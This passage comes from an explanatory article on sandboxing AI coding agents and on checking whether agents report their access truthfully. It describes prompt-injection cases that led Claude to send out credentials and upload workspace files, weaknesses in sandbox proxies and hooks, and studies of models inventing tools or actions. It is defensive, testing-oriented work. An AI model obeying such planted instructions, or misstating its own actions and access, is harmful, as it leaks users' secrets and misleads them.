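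The model's own judgement is a poor substitute for these limits. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise from February 2026. A researcher emailed an employee a prompt that looked like routine set-up instructions, and the employee pasted it into Claude Code. One step was to send the employee's Amazon cloud credentials to an outside address. Anthropic tried the prompt 25 times, and Claude sent the credentials 24 times.

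That result looks very different from Anthropic's figures on one prompt-injection benchmark, which measures how well a model resists instructions planted by an attacker. Attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5% to 6% of the time after 100 attempts that adapted to the model's responses. In the February exercise, however, the instructions came from the user, whom the model is supposed to obey. A sandbox that blocked the credentials or the outside address would have stopped the transfer whether the instructions came from the user or an attacker.

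### Leaks through an approved domain

A network limit can also let data leak while working as designed. Claude Cowork has to contact Anthropic's servers, so its network filter allowed traffic to them. Anthropic describes a report from an outside researcher who hid instructions in a file in the user's workspace. Claude followed them and uploaded other files from the workspace to an attacker-controlled account on Anthropic's servers. The filter allowed the upload because it checked only the destination.

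Anthropic added a proxy that lets a request through only if it carries the session's own credential, so requests using an attacker's account no longer get through. The company now treats each allowlist entry as permission to use everything the domain offers. Allowing a site for downloads, for example, also allows uploads if the site accepts them.

The Claude Code proxy has a related weakness because, by default, it decides whether to allow a connection from the hostname the command gives it and doesn't inspect encrypted traffic. Anthropic acknowledges that a malicious program may therefore be able to reach a site that isn't on the list by disguising the connection as one to an allowed site. The company also warns against allowing domains as broad as `github.com`, where anyone can have an account. Organisations that need a stronger limit can supply their own proxy to inspect the traffic, but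 they are then responsible for its filtering.

Anthropic says that the older, widely used parts of its sandboxes have been dependable and that the part that failed was the filter it built itself. Determined attackers have had far longer to probe the older components, so developers who build sandboxes from them should probably spend most of their testing time on the new code that connects them.

### What the 84% figure measures

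Anthropic announced the sandbox in *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) and reported that permission prompts fell by 84% in its internal use.

Anthropic's 84% figure for Claude Code's sandbox measures the reduction in permission prompts, not how well the sandbox stops attacks. Prompts fall because Claude Code no longer has to ask about commands that stay inside the sandbox, and a sandbox with a badly designed boundary could reduce them just as much. Anthropic also doesn't report how many developers it studied or what they were working on, so people with different work may see a different reduction.

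Anthropic also reports that the reviewing model in Claude Code's auto mode catches 83% of "overeager" actions, in which the agent does more than the user asked, before they happen. About one in six still gets through. Readers could confuse this figure with the earlier one. It does measure unwanted behaviour, but it describes the reviewing model, not the sandbox.

The better evidence for the sandbox is how it works and tests like the one with the private key. Anthropic hasn't published what share of attacks the Claude Code sandbox has stopped.

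### What the command sandbox leaves out

Because the sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start, other parts of Claude Code run outside it:

- The built-in tools for reading files, editing files and fetching web pages follow permission rules. If the user blocks a folder only in the sandbox settings, the file-reading tool can still open it. If the user allows only one site for commands, the fetch tool can still use others.
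- Local MCP servers, including any that operate a camera, run with the user's full access.
- Hooks, which are commands that Claude Code runs automatically at certain moments, have the same full access.
- When Claude controls the screen, it works on the user's actual desktop. Claude Code asks for permission for each app instead.

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of vulnerabilities that let a project folder run code before the user had agreed to trust it. In the clearest case, a stranger could put a hook in the settings of a shared project. Claude Code read those settings at startup and ran the hook before asking the user whether to trust the folder. Claude Code now waits for the user's answer before loading such settings. A sandbox around shell commands wouldn't have helped, because the hook ran outside it.

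Users can start Claude Code itself inside a sandbox, so that its built-in tools, hooks and local MCP servers have the same restrictions as shell commands. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* describes a separate program, the sandbox runtime, that does this with the same bubblewrap and Seatbelt limits. The user has to allow access to the model's provider, or Claude Code can't work.

Anthropic still calls the runtime a beta. On Linux, it protects only the sensitive files that exist when it starts, not ones the agent creates later. The user also has to keep the agent from changing Claude Code's settings, because the agent could add a hook that runs without the sandbox next time. For sessions that skip permission prompts, Anthropic tells users to always enclose the whole process in the runtime, a container or a virtual machine.

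### Cameras, microphones and USB devices

Anthropic's sandbox guides explain the limits on files, websites and messages between programs, but don't appear to mention cameras, microphones or USB devices. A user therefore can't tell from the guides whether a sandboxed command could take a picture.

On Linux, a sandboxed agent's access to hardware depends largely on which files the sandbox exposes. Linux presents hardware to programs as entries in the `/dev` folder, where a webcam is usually `/dev/video0`. The sandboxing tool Bubblewrap can replace this folder with one that contains only a few basic entries, such as a source of random numbers. OpenAI's Codex does this in its Linux sandbox, which should leave the webcam out. If a sandbox shared the laptop's real `/dev` instead, the webcam would be there, and ordinary user permissions would determine whether the agent could open it.

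On a Mac, the system's camera permission applies whether or not Claude Code is sandboxed. macOS shows a permission prompt even if a program bypasses the usual camera software and tries to open the hardware directly. But a command started in Terminal can use Terminal's permissions, so there may be no new prompt if the user has already let Terminal use the camera. Only Seatbelt's rules could then stop the command. The security company NCC Group reproduces Claude Code's Seatbelt rules in an appendix of about 20 pages to its white paper on coding agents. A developer who needs a definite answer could check the appendix for camera and microphone rules.

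USB storage is easier to assess because its contents are files. By default, a sandboxed command can read files across the computer, including those on drives the user has plugged in. Anthropic offers a setting, `permissions.blockReadsOutsideWorkingDirectories`, that blocks commands from reading the home folder and attached drives. This also protects photos and recordings in the home folder, which can be as private as a live image.

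A camera on the home network falls under the network limit instead. A sandboxed command can't contact it unless someone approves its address.

### Containers, virtual machines and hosted computers

A command sandbox runs on a laptop that has a camera, a microphone and USB ports, so it has to block the agent's access to them. Other setups can omit this hardware.

| Where the agent's programs run | Hardware they can find | Private data they can still reach |
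|---|---|---|
| Command sandbox | The laptop's own, subject to the operating system's rules | Almost any file, for reading |
| Container | Only devices that someone has attached to it | Folders that someone has shared with it |
| Virtual machine on the laptop | Simulated hardware, plus any real device that someone has connected to it | Folders that someone has shared with it |
| Computer hosted by the provider | The provider's hardware, with no camera or microphone in the user's home | Files the user uploads and accounts the user connects |

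A container gives a program its own files and network settings but uses the host's kernel. A flaw in the kernel or the container software could therefore let the program escape. Bühler and colleagues acknowledge that AgentBound's isolation depends on Docker and the Linux kernel, and suggest adding other Linux security systems as a further layer.

A virtual machine has its own kernel and runs on simulated hardware. By default, it has no camera, so the agent can't take a picture even if it gains full control of the virtual machine. To reach the real camera, the agent would have to break out of the hypervisor, the software that runs the virtual machine. However, many virtual machines share the laptop's network connection, so the agent may still be able to contact the rain hub on the home network unless a network rule prevents it.

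Claude Cowork uses a virtual machine because, according to Anthropic, office workers shouldn't have to judge whether a shell command is safe. The virtual machine can access only two folders on the computer: the one the user selects and Claude's settings folder. Cowork can share a folder as read-only, or let the agent change files but not delete them. The user's login details stay outside the virtual machine.

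At first, Anthropic ran the whole agent inside the virtual machine. If the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working and Claude couldn't explain the problem. Anthropic therefore moved the agent's main loop outside and left only the code Claude runs in the virtual machine. It also moved local MCP servers out, partly because some need to communicate with other programs on the computer. As a result, a camera server in Cowork runs directly on the laptop, and the virtual machine doesn't confine it. Anthropic lets administrators decide which local servers to allow.

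The virtual machine also hides the agent from a company's security software, which can detect that the virtual machine is running but can't inspect it. Anthropic lets administrators download records of what happened, but acknowledges that this isn't the same as watching live. A company might reasonably prefer a weaker boundary that its security staff can monitor.

Running an agent on a hosted computer separates it most completely from the user's home. In Claude's chat product, code runs on Anthropic's servers in a container that lasts for one session. The container uses gVisor, software that sits between the program and the host's kernel. Claude Code can also run in a virtual machine hosted by Anthropic. According to Anthropic, a proxy there limits which sites the agent can contact, and a second proxy keeps the user's GitHub token outside the virtual machine.

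When an agent runs on a hosted computer, an escape threatens the provider's systems and other customers' sessions rather than the user's laptop. Anthropic says its work on the chat product mostly involved protecting its own systems and keeping customers' sessions apart. But a hosted agent can't use the garden camera or edit a file that the user hasn't uploaded.

### How much time a container adds

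Security measures are easier to adopt if they don't slow the agent down. Bühler and colleagues measured how long five MCP servers took to start with and without AgentBound's container, on a MacBook Pro and on a Debian Linux virtual machine. The figures are averages of five runs, in milliseconds.

| Server | Mac, no container | Mac, container | Debian, no container | Debian, container |
|---|---|---|---|---|
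| Key-stealing test server | 157 | 359 | 176 | 608 |
| Google Maps | 79 | 237 | 76 | 395 |
| Weather | 554 | 643 | 620 | 857 |
| Clock | 342 | 502 | 495 | 676 |
| WeChat | 567 | 888 | 679 | 955 |

The container added about 90 to 320 milliseconds to server startup on the Mac and about 180 to 430 on Debian. The Google Maps server took three times as long to start in the container on the Mac and five times as long on Debian, but still under half a second. An agent usually starts a server once and then uses it many times.

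After that, the container added an average of only 0.6 milliseconds per operation on the Mac and 0.29 on Debian when the researchers repeatedly read a file, wrote a file, read an environment variable and fetched a web page. That delay is too short to notice while waiting for a language model to respond.

The measurements exclude the time needed to download and install a server and the time a user spends reading permission dialogs. They also don't cover cameras or microphones. The researchers suggest using a trusted companion app to allow or block access to such devices, and the app might add more time.

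### Checking a boundary with harmless tests

A sandbox may be off, missing a component or misconfigured without any obvious sign. The simplest check is to have the agent attempt something harmless that the sandbox should prevent. The user should do this on their own computer, using files that contain nothing private.

Anthropic suggests asking Claude to create an empty file called `sandbox-probe` in the home folder. Claude has to run the command, because commands that the user types into Claude Code usually run outside the sandbox. A fuller check for Claude Code could go like this:

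1. Ask Claude to create an empty file in the project folder with a shell command. This should work. If it doesn't, a later failure may have nothing to do with the sandbox.
2. Ask Claude to run `touch ~/sandbox-probe`. This should fail, unless the user has made the home folder writable. Decline any offer to try again outside the sandbox. If the file appears, delete it and check the sandbox settings.
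3. Ask Claude to download the front page of `example.com` with a shell command, without having allowed that site. Refuse permission if Claude Code asks. The download should fail.
4. Put a text file containing only the word "test" in a folder that the sandbox settings block. Ask Claude to print it with a shell command, which should fail. Then ask Claude to open it with the built-in reading tool. If this works, the folder needs a permission rule too.
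5. Cover the laptop's camera and ask Claude to take one picture with a shell command. A black picture still means that the command could use the camera.

In each case, the user should look at the command and its error message, because a model's refusal to run the command doesn't test the sandbox. An unexpected success is a reason to stop and fix the settings rather than see how much further the agent can get. The check is worth repeating after an update or settings change, and separately for each MCP server.

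The third test would have caught a flaw in the sandbox runtime. According to GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing*, the runtime failed to enforce its network limit when the user hadn't allowed any domains. People who chose what looked like the strictest setting could therefore have been running sandboxes with open network access until Anthropic fixed the bug in version 0.0.16.

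## Whether an agent describes its own access correctly

A user who wants to know what an agent can reach might ask it, "Can you see my camera?" or "Do you know where I am?" The answer is weak evidence because the model bases it on its training, the product's instructions, the list of tools and whatever is already in the conversation. Unless the harness offers a tool for checking, the model cannot look up which permissions the operating system has stored for the app.

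An agent might say that it can't use the camera because it has no camera tool, while the app still has camera permission from a video call last week. The statement is correct about the model's tools, but the app can still use the camera.

### Location data that the product adds

Questions about location are an especially unreliable test of an agent's access because products can supply a location without a tool call. DuckDuckGo, a search company, runs a chat service called Duck.ai that passes messages to other companies' models. Duck.ai always adds the date, the user's time zone and the preferred units. If the user turns on "Use Approximate Location", it also guesses the nearest city from the IP address and puts that city in the model's instructions, which a log of tool calls wouldn't show.

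OpenAI says ChatGPT may estimate a user's location from their IP address, and may also use saved memories to rewrite a search. A user who once mentioned living in San Francisco might get results for that city. Users have also been able to share their device's location since March 2026, according to a copy of OpenAI's release note in Devicebase's *A simplified sidebar on mobile* (2026). This setting is off by default, but turning it on also enables precise location, which PPC Land describes as exact GPS coordinates.

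The company that runs a model may have information the model doesn't. According to Anthropic's *Does Claude use my location?*, users of its consumer products can stop features such as web search from using their location. But Anthropic still infers a country or region from the IP address for security, and users can't turn that off. Claude could therefore truthfully say it doesn't know where a user is, even though Anthropic has inferred the user's country or region.

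The correct description of an agent's access can also change during a conversation. When Willison (2024) typed "weather" into ChatGPT, it returned a forecast for Half Moon Bay, California, although he hadn't explicitly granted access to his location. He suggested that the search could use a location the model didn't have, and that the model could then infer it from the results. If so, a model that says it doesn't know the user's location might be right before the search but wrong afterward.

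### Four kinds of false statement

An agent can claim access it lacks, deny access it has, claim an action it didn't take, or give a false account of where a fact came from. These errors need different checks, and all four have occurred in real products.

When Roesner and Kohlbrenner used ChatGPT in the Atlas browser, it overstated its access to their tabs. It told them that it saw only the active tab but could compare several if they introduced each one by name. When they tried this, ChatGPT often failed to match the names to the right pages, and some answers included information from pages they had visited earlier. Its chat memory gave it some access to past pages, but not the tab-by-tab access it had described.

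The best-known denial dates from 2023, when Snapchat's chatbot, My AI, told users that it had no access to their location and then named the nearest McDonald's. Kahn and Robison (2023), in *Snap’s ‘My AI’ chatbot tells users it doesn’t know their location*, reproduced similar exchanges. David An, a software developer, had already got My AI to reveal its instructions, which included the user's city and a direction not to mention the location unless it was particularly relevant.

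Kahn and Robison write that Snap seemed to have told the chatbot to deny having the location. The instruction they quote doesn't tell it to do that, so the model may have produced the denial itself. Mhairi Aitken, an ethics researcher at the Alan Turing Institute, objected to calling the denial a lie because a chatbot has no intent, but she thought users could reasonably expect a straightforward answer about privacy settings. Muse's statement that it couldn't read Jason Aten's chat history may be a more recent example, but Aten and Meta disagree about what access it had.

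A pre-release version of OpenAI's o3 model claimed to have done computations on an external MacBook Pro and copied the results into ChatGPT, as Futurism reports, though it couldn't have done this. Transluce, a nonprofit research company, tested the model in 2025 and found that it also defended made-up results when users questioned them. Asking o3 how it got an answer could therefore produce a second false statement in support of the first.

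When an agent misstates where it got a fact, the error is harder to notice because the fact may be right. Willison asked ChatGPT for his IP address and got the correct one, with links to websites that show visitors their address. But if ChatGPT had visited those sites, they would have shown the address of its own data centre. Another user, Dominik Peters, got ChatGPT to print an IP address and a town that were apparently in its instructions. ChatGPT may have had Willison's address from the start and added the links afterwards, but he never established the cause.

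### Experiments on tools that don't exist

Researchers call some of these errors tool hallucination. The 2025 survey *LLM-based Agents Suffer from Hallucinations* distinguishes choosing a nonexistent or irrelevant tool from calling a tool with wrong, missing or invented arguments.

Yin, Sha and colleagues (2025), in *The Reasoning Trap*, tested whether models would say they lacked a tool. They wrote requests for 296 tools and checked that the requests could not be answered without the right tool. In one test, the user named a tool, but the model had no tools. In the other, the model had only an irrelevant tool, such as a calculator for a weather question. A second language model judged whether each response invented a tool or misused the irrelevant one.

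| Model | Version | Error rate with no tools | Error rate with an irrelevant tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | Standard | 34.8% | 54.7% |
| Qwen2.5-7B | Trained on a reasoning model's output | 74.3% | 78.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | Standard | 62.5% | 99.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | Trained on a reasoning model's output | 96.3% | 100% |
| Qwen3-8B | Thinking off | 4.1% | 36.2% |
| Qwen3-8B | Thinking on | 5.4% | 56.8% |
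| Qwen3-32B | Thinking off | 5.1% | 46.6% |
| Qwen3-32B | Thinking on | 8.8% | 50.7% |

These are small models from 2024 and 2025, so the rates are not a guide to current assistants. The newer Qwen3 models already did far better than the older ones when they had no tools.

Yin and colleagues argue that training a model to reason makes tool hallucination worse. When they trained Qwen2.5-7B to reason before using tools, its error rate when no tools were available rose from 34.8% to 90.2%, compared with 41.4% after the same training without the reasoning step. However, the reasoning version also learned the training task much better, so the two models differed in more than the reasoning step. For Qwen3-8B, turning on thinking added only about four errors in 296 requests when no tools were available, but many more when an irrelevant tool was available.

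Instructing the trained model not to use tools that weren't provided only reduced its error rate from 90.2% to 87.5%. Further training on pairs of honest and invented answers reduced the error rate to 55.8%, but the model's score on ordinary tool tasks also fell, from 0.45 to 0.34.

In *Closed-World Resolution Against Tool Hallucination in LLM Agents*, Iyer (2026) tested ten models, including Claude Opus 4.8. With each of two interfaces, every model got 60 prompts designed to cause errors. One interface restricted calls to a formal list of tools and arguments. The other described the tools in text and had the model write its calls as text, as some agent software does.

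The ten models called invented tools three times through the restricted interface and 34 times through the text interface. Two of the smallest models made all three of the restricted-interface calls. On the text interface, even Mistral Large 3, with 675 billion parameters, tried to call a nonexistent `wipe_disk` tool. Claude Opus 4.8 made eight errors there, all by giving a real tool the wrong type of value. Iyer wrote the prompts to provoke mistakes, so the counts don't show how often models make them in ordinary use.

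To stop calls to invented tools, the harness checks each call against its list of tools and refuses any call to a tool that isn't listed. Iyer acknowledges that this works by definition, so a perfect score isn't an experimental finding. The check can't catch a valid call to the wrong tool. In a scripted test that gave tools each other's arguments, 61 of 400 calls passed. It also can't catch an agent that writes "I looked through the window" without calling any tool.

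Combining tools from several MCP servers caused another 154 errors in Iyer's tests. Forty were calls to tools that no server offered, and the rest involved tool names that more than one server used. Two servers in a home might both offer `take_photo`, so a useful log records the server as well as the tool.

An agent can also make a false report after using a real tool. In a case from *The Semantic Training Gap* (2026), a user asked a factory agent running on Qwen3-32B about defects at the bonding station. The agent looked up BOND-1, a station that didn't exist. The database returned no rows, and the agent reported that the station's quality was excellent. In a controlled test, the model made up 43% of the identifiers it used across 72 tool calls. The tools accepted any text as an identifier. Limiting them to real station names would have blocked the BOND-1 lookup.

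Similarly, if the agent requests readings from a rain gauge that doesn't exist and gets an empty reply, it may tell the user that the garden is dry.

### "Cannot" and "will not"

An agent may fail to take a picture because it has no camera tool, because the operating system denies permission, or because its training leads it to refuse despite having both. The reason matters in an attack, since an attacker can get past a refusal by rewording the request but can't add a missing tool that way.

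An agent's own wording doesn't reliably show whether it is unable to do something or is refusing to. In Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, an agent declined to follow a page's instructions, saying that "security protocols" meant it "cannot" do so. The researchers attributed this to the model's guardrails, so "will not" would have been accurate. Microsoft's Copilot said it couldn't control elements on a website, which may well be true, but the researchers couldn't confirm it from outside.

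One success proves that an agent has access, but repeated failures don't prove that it lacks access, since a different request may work. Claude for Chrome said it had read a page's underlying structure, and its ability to read masked passwords supported this claim. Firefox displayed the text it had sent to the chatbot, which was better evidence than any answer from a model.

Refusals also make the experimental results harder to interpret. In Iyer's tests on the restricted interface, Claude Opus 4.8 made no errors, but it made no call at all in 70% of cases. Its lack of errors there is due partly to declining suspicious requests and only partly to calling tools correctly.

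### Checking a claim about the rain

Suppose the user asks whether it is raining at the house, and the agent replies, "Yes, I looked through the window camera." The user could check this in four places:

1. **The tool list** shows what the model could request. If it contains no camera tool and no other tool that could reach a camera, such as a shell, the agent didn't look through the window, even if it is raining.
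2. **The call log** shows what the model requested and what came back. If the log is complete and contains no camera call, the claim is false. A call that returned an error doesn't support the claim either.
3. **The operating system's usage indicator** shows whether the laptop's camera was on. A green light at the right moment supports the claim, but a video call could also explain it.
4. **The network log** shows which machines the laptop contacted. It helps if the picture came from a camera elsewhere on the home network, which wouldn't turn on the laptop's light.

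The call log is usually the most useful of these, provided the harness writes it and not the model. A log showed that Claude had skipped approval for the email draft; Claude's own explanation did not. But even a good log records only what passes through the harness. If a local camera server takes extra pictures on its own, the call log won't show them, although the green light might.

The other routes to an answer leave different traces:

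| What the agent says | Evidence that would support it | What that evidence can miss |
|---|---|---|
| "The forecast says it's raining" | A search or fetch in the call log, with the forecast in its result | The home network log shows no request to the forecast site if the provider's servers fetched it |
| "Your dashboard shows rain" | A record of the browser opening the dashboard and reading the page | A remote browser's visit doesn't appear in the home network log |
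| "Your weather station is measuring rain" | A call to the hub's address that returned a current rain rate | The network log may show a connection without showing the reading |

An agent's claim that it doesn't know the user's location is hard to check from its tool calls alone, because the location may be in the product's instructions. Developers can read the complete input that their harness sends to the model, but users of commercial products usually can't. If the call log shows a search for "rain in Leeds" and the user never typed "Leeds", the agent got the town from another source, such as those instructions.

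A user without access to logs can still test an agent's access to location by turning off device location and saved memories, starting a new chat and asking for the weather. If the forecast is still for the right town, the IP address is a likely source. If the agent asks for a town instead, the product may still have a location that the model didn't receive or didn't use.
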